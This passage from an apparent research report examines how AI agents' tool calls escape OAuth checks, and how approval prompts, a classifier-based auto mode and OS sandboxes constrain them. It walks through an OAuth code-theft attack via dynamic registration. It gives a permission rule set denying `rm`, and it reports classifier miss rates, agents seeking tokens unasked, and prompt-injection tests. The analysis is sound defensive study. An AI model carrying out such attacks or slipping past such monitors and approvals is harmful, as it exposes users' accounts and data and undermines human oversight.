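Python scripts and Docker commands are just as hard to classify. Docker runs programs in isolated containers, and a command might start a test database on the laptop or download software from the internet. About 84% of Claude's shell calls start more than one program, so a call that begins with a search can also upload data.

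Calls that reach a service with an inherited credential are therefore probably a small minority of coding agents' calls. They still carry a substantial part of the risk, because a single `git push` to the wrong place can do more harm than thousands of text searches.

### From coding to agents in general

Estimating the share for all agents requires knowing how much of their work is coding. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) analyzed a random sample of 998,481 tool calls made through the company's public API, which other companies use to build agents on its models. A Claude model sorted the calls by field. Nearly 50% were in software engineering, and no other field, such as customer service, sales or finance, accounted for more than a few percent.

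Other data also put coding at about half. *How are AI agents used?* (Stein, 2026), a study from the UK AI Security Institute, compares several sources. Computing and mathematical work made up 51.7% of use of Anthropic's API in November 2025. On OpenRouter, a marketplace that offers models from many companies, programming made up 58% of tokens from May to November 2025. That figure includes a lot of text unrelated to agents, since tool calls accounted for only about 15% of OpenRouter's tokens by late 2025.

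A simple estimate multiplies Anthropic's figure for coding by the share of the three most common tools:

0.5 × 0.85 = 0.425

On this estimate, about 43% of all agent tool calls are shell or file operations by coding agents, and so are outside OAuth. But the two numbers do not really belong together, for several reasons:

- They describe different agents. Anthropic's sample covers thousands of companies' own agents, while the 85% comes from a research group's use of Claude Code and Codex. An agent that a company runs on its own servers may use quite different tools from one on a laptop.
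- "Software engineering" is a field of work, not a way of reaching a service. It can include closing an issue through a remote MCP server. Agents in other fields also run code, for example to analyze sales data.
- The figures come from different periods. Anthropic's calls date from late 2025 and early 2026, when agents were less capable than they are now and companies outside software had less experience with them.
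- Some of Anthropic's calls were tests. The company could not separate real work from evaluations, and it believes that many of the apparent data thefts in the sample were evaluations.

The estimate also covers only the three most common tools. The Copilot data gives a better figure for coding, 95%. Since coding is half of agent use, coding calls outside OAuth make up 0.5 × 0.95, or about 48%, of the total. The overall share outside OAuth enforcement would be about 48% if all the calls in the other half were inside it, 73% if half were, and 98% if none were.

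The true share is probably well above the bottom of that range. For example, a company's customer service agent may look up orders with a key that belongs to the company. No customer or employee has given that agent a grant, so OAuth does not govern its calls. This is only a guess, because Anthropic does not report which credentials its customers' agents use.

Counting calls also gives coding a lot of weight, because a coding agent may make dozens of calls to finish one job. Anthropic says its sample overrepresents this kind of work for that reason. *Understanding KV Residency in Production-Scale Agentic LLM Workloads* (2026) reports 121 million model calls in 13.9 million sessions for Microsoft 365's agents and chat assistant, and 761 million in 13.5 million sessions for Copilot's coding agent. The coding agent made about six times as many calls in a similar number of sessions.

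Coding is a minority of agent use in some settings. *From LLM Inference to Agentic Workloads* (2026) analyzes one day of traffic from three applications. A search agent had 141,376 sessions, about four times the coding agent's 35,037. An assistant similar to OpenClaw, an open-source personal agent, had 2,386.

Giving more weight to search would probably not lower the share outside OAuth by much, because reading public web pages requires no credential. Giving more weight to office assistants could lower it more. Microsoft, for example, controls both Microsoft 365 and its own agent that works inside it, so it can check the agent's access separately if it chooses to.

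These counts don't weight calls by how much they matter. Anthropic estimates that 0.8% of the actions in its sample were irreversible, such as sending an email to a customer. OAuth checks on those few calls could be more useful than checks on most of the others, so a service adding checks could reasonably start there.

### Browser agents

Almost everything a browser agent does is outside OAuth enforcement, because it uses either the user's cookie or no credential at all. There is no public count of how often people use browser agents or how many of the agents' visits are to logged-in accounts.

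The best available figures describe the kinds of work people do with Perplexity's Comet. In data from July to October 2025 that Stein converted to standard occupational groups, computing and mathematical work made up 30.4% of queries, office and administrative work 5.0%, and education 4.4%. The computing and mathematical share was much higher for Anthropic's API, at 51.7%, which suggests that people use browser agents for a wider range of tasks.

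The underlying study also lists the websites Comet visited most often, such as google.com, but the list doesn't show whether users were logged in. A visit to google.com could be an ordinary search or the first step towards someone's email. The data are more than a year old, and several companies have released or improved browser agents since then.

Downloads suggest that browser use is growing. Stein tracked public MCP servers and found that general-purpose ones, which can operate a browser or a whole computer, rose from 41% to 50% of downloads between November 2024 and early 2026. Microsoft's Playwright server, a popular example, lets an agent control a browser. But developers often use Playwright to test their own websites in a fresh browser with no saved logins, so download counts don't measure how many agents act inside people's real accounts.

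### Remote MCP servers on the public internet

Researchers can measure remote servers more directly, because they can connect to a server over the internet and see whether it requires a login. Zhou and colleagues, at Fudan University and Central South University, searched for these servers with FOFA and Shodan, two search engines that index internet devices and services. They found 28,715 candidates after removing duplicates. They then sent each one the opening message of an MCP connection, and 7,973 replied validly. Two researchers checked a random sample of 100 and found only one that was not an MCP server.

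| How the server checks callers | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| No authentication | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| OAuth | 2,428 | 30.45% |
| Static token or API key | 2,312 | 29.00% |

About 70% of the servers therefore did not use OAuth. Among those that required a credential, OAuth and static keys were almost equally common. OAuth was much more common than in Skverer's study (8.5%), which included many local servers.

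The share of servers with no authentication, 40.55%, is a poor measure of how much private data is exposed. Zhou and colleagues examined a random sample of these open servers and found that most were tests or demonstrations without sensitive data. But one exposed a company's internal customer database, where anyone could query more than 5,000 records with names, phone numbers and addresses without logging in.

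The scan also counts each server once, so a student's abandoned demo counts as much as a server with a million users. Large companies' servers are probably more likely to use OAuth, so the share of remote calls that go through OAuth could be well above 30%. The scan also misses servers on companies' private networks, and it may still include some duplicates. When the team later examined 1,118 of the OAuth servers, it set aside 387 as redundant, for example because the same server appeared under several addresses.

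A more recent audit found even less OAuth. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) searched eleven sources in July 2026, including package registries, MCP directories and records of website certificates. It confirmed 640 servers and ran active security tests on 414 of them, of which 91.8% had no OAuth. Across the confirmed servers, it counted 687 tools that could run shell commands without any access controls.

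The audit's 91.8% and the scan's 70% don't necessarily conflict. Padilla looked in places where individual developers publish their work, including cloud platforms that give each project a public web address. A server that requires a login is also harder to test, so the 414 may include too many open ones. Many of the servers were short-lived, so few people can have come to depend on them. Of those he confirmed in one round of measurements, 41.6% were missing from the next round three days later.

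These servers can still cause harm while they are online. Padilla found 68 vulnerabilities serious enough to report, including one that let an outsider send commands to a database. If a server runs shell commands for anyone who calls it, an attacker can use it without involving an agent or a user. OAuth, or even a simple password, would keep out most strangers.

### Flaws in the OAuth that servers use

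A server that uses OAuth can still let the wrong person in. Zhou and colleagues tested 119 of the OAuth servers and found 325 flaws, with at least one in each server. Most of the flaws are in how a program gets a grant, which happens before the service checks any token.

The most common problems involve dynamic client registration. This is an automatic way for a program to introduce itself to an authorization server. The program sends some details about itself, including the address where it wants to receive the authorization code, and gets an identifier in return. It is convenient because an agent program can connect to a new server without its developers having to arrange anything in advance. But if the server accepts any address from anyone, an attacker can use it as follows:

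1. The attacker registers a program under a familiar name, with a return address that the attacker controls.
2. The attacker sends the user a link to the server's real login page.
3. The user logs in, sees the familiar name and approves the request.
4. The authorization server sends the code to the attacker's address, and the attacker exchanges it for a token.

PKCE does not stop this attack. It protects a code that someone else intercepts, but here the attacker started the login and already has the secret needed to redeem the code. The token is then valid and the user did approve the grant, so the service's later checks all succeed.

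Registration flaws affected 96.6% of the tested servers. A second group of flaws affected 85.7% and arises because agent programs run on users' own machines and cannot keep a permanent secret. Some servers accepted logins without PKCE. Others did not show the user where the authorization code would go, which makes a suspicious request harder to notice.

Of the 119 servers, 81 also used a second OAuth login to reach another company's service. Each login can be secure by itself while the connection between them is weak. For example, a server might require PKCE from the agent program but leave it out of its own request to the second service. A server might also store the final return address in a value that an attacker can change, and then send the authorization code to the wrong address.

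All 119 tested servers had a flaw, but this does not show that every OAuth server has one. The 119 were about 5% of the 2,428 servers that the scan found, and they were not chosen at random. The team started with the 1,118 servers that advertised dynamic registration, because each of the others would have required manual work to test. It then removed duplicates, servers that did not respond properly, and 316 with strict company access controls. The remaining servers let almost any program register, which is the feature behind the most common flaws.

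The tests seem reliable. The researchers checked all 379 of their software's alerts by hand and rejected 54. They did not carry out full attacks on real users' data, so the results show which protections were missing, but not how often attackers have exploited those gaps. Nine of the problems now have entries in the public register of software vulnerabilities.

Since November 2025, MCP's preferred identifier has been one based on a web address, with dynamic registration kept mainly for older software. This should make it harder for an attacker to use a well-known program's name, because they would also need to control that program's web address. The change won't help until servers adopt it and stop accepting anonymous registrations.

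Because of these flaws, the 30.45% of servers with OAuth is an upper limit on the share whose OAuth works as intended. The flaws don't make static keys safer than OAuth overall. A static key has no login page for an attacker to misuse, but it also has no consent page and often no expiry date.

### Local servers, transports and downloads

Local servers have no public address, so internet scans can't find them. Researchers have to estimate their number from published code and download counts. *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (Guo, Hao and colleagues, 2025) collected 17,630 listings from six MCP marketplaces and found that fewer than half were valid projects. The rest included placeholders and abandoned work, so the marketplaces' advertised totals are a poor guide to how many servers people can use.

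The team also examined 341 client programs that connect to MCP servers. Of these, 56.9% used SSE, an older way of connecting over HTTP, and 38.1% used stdio. MCP's OAuth procedure applies only to HTTP, so the 56.9% is closer to an upper limit on the share using OAuth than an estimate of it. Authorization is optional over HTTP, and the scan by Zhou and colleagues suggests that most remote servers don't use OAuth. The figures also count programs rather than use, so a hobby project counts as much as a popular code editor.

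It is hard to find out which servers people connect to in practice. Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications*, analyzed 1,723 applications on GitHub that use MCP and found that 85.2% keep their list of servers in a file, but the file has no standard name. Researchers can automatically count the packages that ordinary software depends on because they are listed in a standard format, but MCP has no similar format for listing servers.

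Stein's study has the most data on what developers install. It covers 177,436 tools on 19,388 public MCP servers, published between November 2024 and February 2026. For 3,854 of the servers, Stein could also find download counts from npm and PyPI, the JavaScript and Python package registries. Monthly downloads rose from about 80,000 in January 2025 to 14 million in February 2026. Servers mainly for software development and other computing work accounted for 90% of downloads.

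These registries are the usual way to distribute local servers, so the downloads show that local servers have grown very quickly. The downloads cannot show what share of MCP use is local, because a user who adds a ready-made connector in a chatbot's settings downloads nothing from npm or PyPI. These hosted connectors are probably among the most likely to use OAuth, so the data leave out much of the use that OAuth does govern.

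Downloads are also an imperfect measure of use. An automated system that sets up a new virtual machine every hour may download the same server each time, while a developer may download it once and use it for months. Stein warns that the figures may mostly reflect what developers are trying out. As a check, he compared them with usage counts from Smithery, a marketplace that also offers remote servers. Computing tools made up 80% of use there and 90% of the registry downloads, so the downloads seem to overrepresent developers somewhat.

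Stein's data show that agents increasingly change things instead of only reading them. Tools that take actions, such as editing files, sending emails or clicking buttons, rose from 27% to 65% of downloads over the period. The number of public servers that can make payments rose from 47 in January 2025 to 1,578 in February 2026. If many of these servers use static keys, as Skverer's results suggest, calls outside OAuth may be increasing in both number and consequence.

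### Counting organizations

The share of organizations with any agents working outside OAuth is a different measure from the share of agent use outside it. Among organizations whose developers use coding agents on their own machines, that share is probably close to 100%, because a single agent that edits a local file is enough to count. It would be more useful to count the organizations where agents can reach important accounts with inherited credentials. A company would belong to that group if even one developer's agent could use a saved cloud login, even if every official connection used OAuth.

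Surveys of organizations also give different results from counts of tool calls. Stein summarizes a survey of 306 people who build or run agents. Of the 69 who said where they used agents, 48% named technology and 44% named finance and banking. In Anthropic's sample of tool calls, finance made up no more than a few percent. Both can be true if many banks have agents that make relatively few calls. A bank's agent may also be able to move money, so a count of calls could greatly understate its importance.

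### The estimates compared

| What the figure counts | Share outside OAuth | Based on | Main sources of bias |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool calls by Claude Code and Codex | About 99% or more | 432,510 calls by 43 developers (Zhu and colleagues) | One research group's own use. Most of the calls involve no service. |
| Tool calls by Copilot in an editor | About 95% or more | 774.7 million calls in one week (Liu and colleagues) | United States only. The records may leave out some MCP tools. |
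| Tool calls by all agents | At least 43% to 48% from coding alone, and possibly up to 98% | 998,481 API calls (Anthropic), combined with the data on coding agents | The samples cover different agents and periods. The credentials in the other half are unknown. |
| Actions by browser agents | Nearly 100%, by definition | No public count of actions | The amount of use in logged-in accounts is unknown. |
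| Remote MCP servers in an internet scan | About 70% | 7,973 live servers (Zhou and colleagues) | Many demos and some duplicates. Popular servers count no more than unused ones. |
| Remote MCP servers in a security audit | About 92% | 414 servers (Padilla) | Many short-lived projects, and probably too many open servers. |
| MCP client programs | At least 38%, if those on stdio have no OAuth login of their own | 341 programs (Guo and colleagues) | Data from 2025. Using HTTP does not mean using OAuth. |
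| Downloads of MCP servers | No estimate possible | 3,854 servers with download counts (Stein) | Mostly local servers. Hosted connectors are missing, and automated downloads count. |

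## Asking the user, or a second model, before each action

When no service decides whether an agent may act, the agent program can still stop and ask the user before each action. This question is called an approval prompt, and most agent products have one. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) examined 21 agent systems as of April 2026 and found that 15 ask for approval while the agent works, 14 let users write rules, and 16 let users set boundaries such as permitted folders.

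### From a proposed command to a decision

Claude Code combines prompts with rules. According to Anthropic's documentation, a shell command in its Manual mode goes through these steps:

1. The model produces a tool call that contains the command.
2. If operators such as `&&` or `;` join several commands together, Claude Code splits them and checks each part.
3. It compares the parts with the user's deny rules, then the ask rules, then the allow rules. The first match decides, so a narrow allow rule can't make an exception to a broad deny rule.
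4. If no rule matches, Claude Code runs the command only if it is on a built-in list of read-only commands, such as `ls` and `grep`. Otherwise it shows a prompt.
5. The prompt displays the command and a short description. The user can approve it once, approve it and stop further questions about similar commands, or refuse.
6. If the user chooses not to be asked again, Claude Code saves a new allow rule in a settings file, and the rule applies to later sessions in the same repository. For file edits, this choice lasts only until the session ends.

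A small rule set might look like this, where `*` stands for any text:

```json
"permissions": {
  "allow": ["Bash(npm test *)", "Bash(git commit *)"],
  "ask":   ["Bash(git push *)"],
  "deny":  ["Bash(rm *)"]
}
```

| Proposed command | What Claude Code does |
|---|---|
| `npm test` | Runs it without a prompt, because an allow rule matches |
| `git commit -m "Fix login" && git push` | Shows a prompt. An allow rule covers the first part, but the second part matches the ask rule. |
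| `npm test && rm -r build` | Refuses the whole command, because the second part matches the deny rule |

Claude Code enforces these rules itself, so a prompt injection that misleads the model does not change them. But the rules match the text of a command, and a differently worded command can often run the same program. Anthropic therefore warns that a rule for shell commands isn't a security boundary around a program. The user's judgment has a similar weakness, since studies such as *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) have found that what an agent does can differ from the text the user approved.

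### How approval differs from OAuth consent

An approval normally covers one action, and the agent program enforces it without informing the service. The prompt can look much like an OAuth consent page, but an OAuth grant covers a class of operations and is enforced by the service.

Suppose the agent proposes `gh issue close 42`. GitHub receives nothing unless the user approves. If they do, `gh` sends an ordinary request with the same token and the same broad `repo` scope as before. GitHub's records can't show whether anyone agreed to that particular request.

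The prompt can be more specific than the OAuth grant, applying to a single item such as issue 42, and it also works for actions that involve no service, such as deleting a local file.

When the agent remembers a user's approval, that approval works more like an OAuth grant, because a rule like `npm test *` covers a class of commands. The user can also turn off nearly all prompts, as in Claude Code's `bypassPermissions` mode, although deny rules still apply. An OAuth token would keep its limits in that mode.

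### How people answer the prompts

Claude Code users accept almost all permission prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gave an acceptance rate of 93% in March 2026, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* gave 97% in August 2026. Most prompts probably concern routine commands that a careful person would also accept, so these rates don't prove carelessness. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for approval, but only 3% of individual permission requests. This may suggest that users examine plans more carefully, though they can also reject a plan because it is a poor approach rather than a dangerous one.

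Many users also arrange to see fewer prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written an allow rule for shell commands by hand. These rules are often broad. Anthropic reports that 5% allow every shell command and another 43% allow programs such as Python, which can run almost any code. A quarter of interactive sessions started in bypass mode. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* collected 290 reports of file damage, 80 of which involved automatic approval.

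Users choose automatic approval more often as they gain experience. Anthropic found in a February 2026 study that people with fewer than 50 Claude Code sessions used full automatic approval in roughly 20% of sessions. By about 750 sessions, the share was over 40%.

About 80% of the API tool calls in the same study's sample came from agents that appeared to have at least one safeguard, such as restricted permissions or required approval. A person seemed to be involved in some way in 73% of the calls. Both figures are upper bounds, because the Claude model that classified the calls sometimes found human involvement where there was none. Neither figure shows that anyone approved the particular call. Human involvement was lower for complex tasks (67%) than for the simplest ones (87%), probably in part because approving each step becomes impractical as the number of steps grows.

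*Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 107 practitioners about permission requests. Of these, 47.7% said they read the requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim them, and 20.6% said they approve by default. A third said they had become less careful over time, but 76.6% said they look more closely at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges.

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one type of agent action without close review. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, the figure was 61%. This matters for credentials because an agent can read a secret or send data elsewhere without leaving any trace in the code it delivers. About 21% often approved reading secrets or other sensitive files without close review, and 36% often approved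 access to the internet or connected tools without it.

Developers who had heard of a security or privacy problem with agents were more likely to approve without close review (70%) than those who hadn't (43%). The gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, but the two groups may differ in other ways, so the result doesn't show that learning about incidents makes people careless.

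### Is approval just theatre?

Wang and colleagues write that frequent prompts turn users into "OK-button machines". This comes close to calling the prompts security theatre, meaning a measure that looks protective but does little.

The strongest evidence that users often approve dangerous commands comes from a study for which Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor. Partway through each coding session, one approval prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

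Three things weaken this result somewhat. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a developer at work. Anthropic published the result in a post explaining why prompts would no longer be the default. And the testers who got through 50 prompts may have been the ones who clicked fastest, which could explain part of the drop. Still, a refusal rate of 13.6% for clearly dangerous commands is very low.

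Code review shows a similar trend. *Habituation at the Gate* (2026) followed 400 people through 11,429 reviews of code changes proposed by agents. As reviewers gained experience, their approval rate for these changes rose by 14.5 percentage points and they wrote fewer comments. Their approval rate for changes proposed by people fell over the same period. Better agents could explain the rise, although the study links it to each reviewer's experience rather than to the date.

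In another experiment, approval prompts stopped many of the actions that users had not asked for. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages. People who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of these overreaching actions and allowed 94.1% of the actions the task required.

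These people may have refused so much more often than Anthropic's testers because Yan's prompts were fewer and clearer. There were only 18, and each described the action in plain language, including the amount or recipient, while a developer may see hundreds of prompts containing shell commands. The two studies also measured different things. A lounge pass is easy to understand, and approving one isn't always a mistake because some people want it. A destructive command may be hard to recognize. The comparison suggests that prompts work better when they are rare and describe consequences, but neither experiment tested this directly.

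Letting people write rules in advance did not solve the problem. Another group in Yan's experiment set a rule of allow, ask or never for each of four categories, such as spending money. They chose "ask" for 81% of the rules, so most decisions still led to prompts. They then blocked about 20 percentage points less overreach than the people who were asked to approve every action. Of the 148 unwanted actions that ran, people had explicitly approved 133. Perhaps writing the rules made people feel they had already dealt with the risk, but the study doesn't establish the cause.

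Users also interrupt agents, which is the other argument against calling oversight theatre. Anthropic found that new users of Claude Code interrupt it in about 5% of turns (a turn is one stretch of work by the agent), while experienced users, who approve more automatically, interrupt it in about 9%. In Salerno and colleagues' survey, 69.2% of respondents said they interrupt, redirect or stop agents. In Wu and colleagues' survey, 57% of developers said they watch the output and intervene when needed.

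Interruptions show that users supervise the work, but not that they catch dangerous actions. Users most often interrupted Claude Code to supply missing technical context or a correction (32%), and next most often because it was slow, stuck or excessive (17%). In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 65% of developers had stepped in because the agent misunderstood the task, and only 34% because it was about to run a risky or destructive command. An interruption may also come too late, since a user can undo a bad edit but not a sent email.

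So the charge seems mostly right about long sessions with a prompt before every command, but mostly wrong about a few clear questions on serious actions. Anthropic argues from its usage data that regulators shouldn't require approval of every action, because this would add friction without necessarily making anyone safer. Anthropic has a commercial interest in that conclusion because it sells autonomous agents, but the experiments broadly support it. They don't support removing every prompt. If only about 0.8% of actions are irreversible, as Anthropic estimates, an agent program that could reliably identify them would rarely need to interrupt the user. A sandbox can also reduce prompts, because the agent needs less supervision inside it.

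### Letting a second model decide

An automatic approver is software, usually a language model, that decides on the user's behalf whether an action may run. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) introduced one in March as a preview. Auto mode became the default on most individual and team plans in August. According to Anthropic's current documentation, interactive terminal sessions start in auto mode on every plan unless the user or organization has chosen otherwise. In April, Wang and colleagues wrote that no deployed system relied on a model alone to judge whether an action was safe, which is no longer true for many of Claude Code's shell commands.

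Anthropic describes the process roughly as follows:

1. Deny and ask rules still apply, and so do narrow allow rules. Claude Code sets aside allow rules that could run any code, such as one for all Python commands.
2. Tools that only read, and edits to files inside the project, go ahead without review.
3. Other actions, including most shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools, go to a second model called the classifier.
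4. The classifier first gives a quick yes or no, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags the action, it examines the same material again and reasons about it before deciding.
5. If it still blocks the action, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer way. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. This prevents the agent from using explanations to influence the classifier's decision, and keeps text planted in a web page from reaching the classifier directly. A separate check scans tool results for prompt injection and warns the agent. But without the tool results, the classifier can't check some details of an action. If the agent wants to cancel job `abc123`, for example, the classifier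 can't determine whether that ID came from a search or the agent made it up.

Two of Anthropic's examples involve inherited credentials. In one, an agent hit a login error and began searching environment variables and settings files for other tokens. In the other, an agent prepared a command to publish a script as a GitHub gist in order to share it for debugging. The `gh` token always includes the `gist` scope, so GitHub would accept the request. The classifier is meant to block it because the user never asked to publish anything.

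Anthropic has published several measurements of how often the classifier lets a dangerous action through:

| Test | Dangerous actions missed |
|---|---|
| 52 real actions in which an agent overstepped its instructions (March) | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out (March) | 5.7% |
| The dangerous commands from the study of 1,053 testers (August) | 11% |
| Synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, an AI safety company, after improvements (August) | 7% |

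False alarms were rare. On 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's employees, the classifier blocked 0.4% of harmless actions, or about one in 250.

The 17% figure comes closest to ordinary use, but it is based on only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented. For example, a user who says "Clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) has not clearly agreed to the agent overwriting the shared history. Better models may reduce this error, but some instructions are ambiguous, and only the user can clarify those.

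The August results favor auto mode over prompts. Auto mode blocked 89% of the commands in the study, while people refused 13.6%. Anthropic also re-examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. It found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This evidence is weaker because users choose their mode and may choose differently for risky work, and because a model did the grading.

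OpenAI's Codex has a similar feature called Auto-review. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test both products in July against 72 prompt injection scenarios, with ten attempts at each. No attack succeeded against the three Claude models in auto mode, but we can't infer much about auto mode's own contribution because only 0.09% of attacks succeeded without it. For OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, the success rate was 5.83% with Auto-review and 19.03% with full access and no review, so Auto-review seems to have stopped about two thirds of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. Both companies have since released newer models, and OpenAI had already updated Auto-review by the time Anthropic published the results.

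Wang and colleagues object to this whole approach, arguing that an attacker who can mislead the agent's model may also be able to mislead the model that checks it, and that a user's request rarely contains everything needed to judge an action. Both points are reasonable, and the second matches Anthropic's account of the misses. But they are reasons to reject automatic approval only if the alternative is a person who pays attention. Anthropic says that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every action carefully, and recommends manual review for high-stakes changes to production systems.

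Ask rules still produce a prompt in auto mode, so developers can combine the two methods, leaving routine commands to the classifier and still approving each `git push` or deployment themselves.

### Judging the effects of a command

A classifier that reads only the conversation and the command has to guess what the command will do. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, built a system called Caper that runs the command first and decides afterwards:

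1. Caper takes a snapshot of the isolated workspace in which the agent is working.
2. It runs the command there with the network switched off and records what happens. The agent doesn't see the output yet.
3. It reduces the record to a short report of changed files, attempted connections, output, and any credentials or other protected files that the command read.
4. A model compares the report with the user's task.
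5. If the model approves, Caper keeps the result and gives the agent the output. If not, Caper restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

In one test, the user asked for a database migration, but the agent's command also deleted three tables. Claude Code's auto mode allowed the command. Caper's model blocked it because Caper's report showed that the database had shrunk from 32 KB to 20 KB. The agent then backed up the database and ran only the migration script.

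The team compared Caper with six existing systems on two sets of tasks. SABER has 682 development tasks in which a careless or misled agent can cause harm. YoloFS-Ext has 102 tasks that run a harmful tool, each paired with a safe task that has the same request and command.

| System | Harmful outcomes on SABER | Harmful outcomes on YoloFS-Ext |
|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% |
| Six existing systems | 14.8% to 21.2% | 35.3% to 94.1% |
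| Claude Code's auto mode (one of the six) | 14.8% | 62.7% |
| Caper | 6.7% | 7.8% |

The team ran auto mode with a Chinese model as the agent and an OpenAI model as the classifier, so the results don't describe the product as people normally use it. The comparison is still fair to both methods, because the team used the same models when it replaced Claude Code's built-in classifier with Caper's check. With that change, harmful outcomes fell to 10.0% on SABER and 6.9% on YoloFS-Ext.

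The main benefit of observing effects seems to be fewer false alarms. Without the report of observed effects, Caper's own model reduced harmful outcomes on YoloFS-Ext to 17.6%, but it also blocked 61.8% of the safe tasks. When the model predicted the effects instead, harmful outcomes fell to 3.9%, which is lower than Caper's rate, but it still blocked 61.8% of the safe tasks. With the real report, it blocked only 1.0%. A model can prevent a lot of harm by refusing anything uncertain, but users would probably switch it off.

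Caper's model takes a median of 3.2 seconds to decide, about as long as the same model needs without the report. The sandbox adds roughly half a second to each approved command and 1.5 seconds to each blocked one. On SABER, the agent safely completed 48.6% of tasks with Caper and 57.4% with no approval at all, because it stopped or declined more often with Caper. Wu and colleagues didn't test attackers who adapt to Caper, for example by making a harmful program do nothing harmful during the trial run.

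The approach is hardest to use for commands that reach a service. A snapshot can restore a deleted file, but it can't reopen a GitHub issue or recall a leaked credential. Caper therefore has to run commands without a network connection, so a command like `gh issue close 42` would fail. The team suggests sending such requests to a stand-in that records them and returns placeholder answers. An approver could then see what the command would have sent, but not what GitHub would have done with it.

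## Confining the agent with the operating system

An approval prompt determines whether a command may start, while a sandbox limits what it can do as it runs, even if the user approved the command without reading it. VS Code's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents* treats the two separately, and many coding agents now offer both.

### What a sandbox enforces

To open a file or a network connection, a program must make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel normally checks the request against the user's permissions, so an agent's command gets whatever access the developer has. Inside a sandbox, the command must also satisfy a narrower set of rules.

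These operating system rules also apply to every program that a command starts, as Wiesen explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*. A Python script that tries to delete a folder therefore meets the same limits as `rm`, whereas a rule that matches the text of a command could miss the script.

Most sandboxes have rules for reading files, writing files and connecting to the network. The default rules usually restrict writing much more than reading. Claude Code's sandbox lets commands write to the project folder and a temporary folder, but they can read almost the whole computer, including files that contain credentials. Codex can also read files almost anywhere. Copilot CLI's sandbox doesn't open the whole home folder. But by default it lets commands read the settings of developer tools, including tokens for package registries, according to GitHub's *Configuring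 local sandbox settings*.

The file and network rules depend on each other. Anthropic warns that without network limits, a misled agent could send out the user's SSH keys. Without file limits, it could alter the system to get network access back.

Some files inside the project need protection too. Agent programs load settings from the project folder, and Git can run scripts, called hooks, from the `.git` folder. If a sandboxed command could write a hook, the hook might later run outside the sandbox. Claude Code therefore blocks writes to its own settings files, Git's hooks and configuration, and shell startup files in the project. NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, considers blocking writes to configuration files mandatory.

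Codex makes the whole `.git` folder read-only, which is safer than leaving it writable, as Copilot CLI does. But `git commit` has to write to that folder, so Codex must run it outside the sandbox.

### The mechanisms

macOS includes a mechanism called Seatbelt. The agent program writes a profile, which lists the files and connections a command may use, and starts the command under that profile. Cursor's *Agent Sandboxing* points out that Chrome and Apple's own applications rely on Seatbelt too.

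On Linux, products combine several tools, including bubblewrap, which starts a command in its own namespaces. These give the command a separate view of the machine. It can find only the folders that bubblewrap includes, and bubblewrap can make some of them read-only. Bubblewrap can also give the command a private network with no outside connection.

Landlock restricts which folders a command can access without changing the command's view of the machine. A program gives the kernel a list of the folders it needs, and the kernel blocks its access to the rest. Neither the program nor any program it starts can lift this restriction later.

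Seccomp filters system calls, so it can block those that open network connections. It can't allow one file and refuse another, because the filter can't read the file's path. Products therefore use it alongside bubblewrap or Landlock. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) described Codex as using Landlock for files and seccomp for the network. Codex has since switched to bubblewrap and seccomp, and OpenAI's *Permissions* lists Landlock as a fallback.

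In September 2025, Windows had no ready-made confinement mechanism that suited a coding agent such as Codex. AppContainer is for applications whose needs are known in advance, while an agent may run any developer tool. Windows Sandbox opens a separate, disposable desktop, but the agent has to work on the developer's real files.

Wiesen's first design didn't need administrator rights. It pointed the usual network settings at a dead address, which stopped many tools but not programs that ignored them. The final design creates two extra Windows accounts and uses the firewall to block one of them from the network. Commands run under these accounts, and Windows allows a write only if both the account and a separate sandbox identity have permission.

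Copilot uses Microsoft's MXC, which gives it one interface to the mechanisms of all three operating systems. GitHub (2026) released the local sandbox as a public preview in June. *Microsoft eXecution Container (MXC)* quotes a warning from Microsoft's early preview that nobody should yet treat MXC profiles as security boundaries. Some early gaps have since closed. For example, supported versions of Windows can now block access to chosen folders, and on other versions the command fails instead of running without the block.

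Containers and virtual machines can hold a whole working environment. A container has its own files and list of processes but shares the host's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel could let a program escape. In claude.ai, Anthropic's chat service, Claude runs code in a container with gVisor, which adds a layer between the program and the host's kernel.

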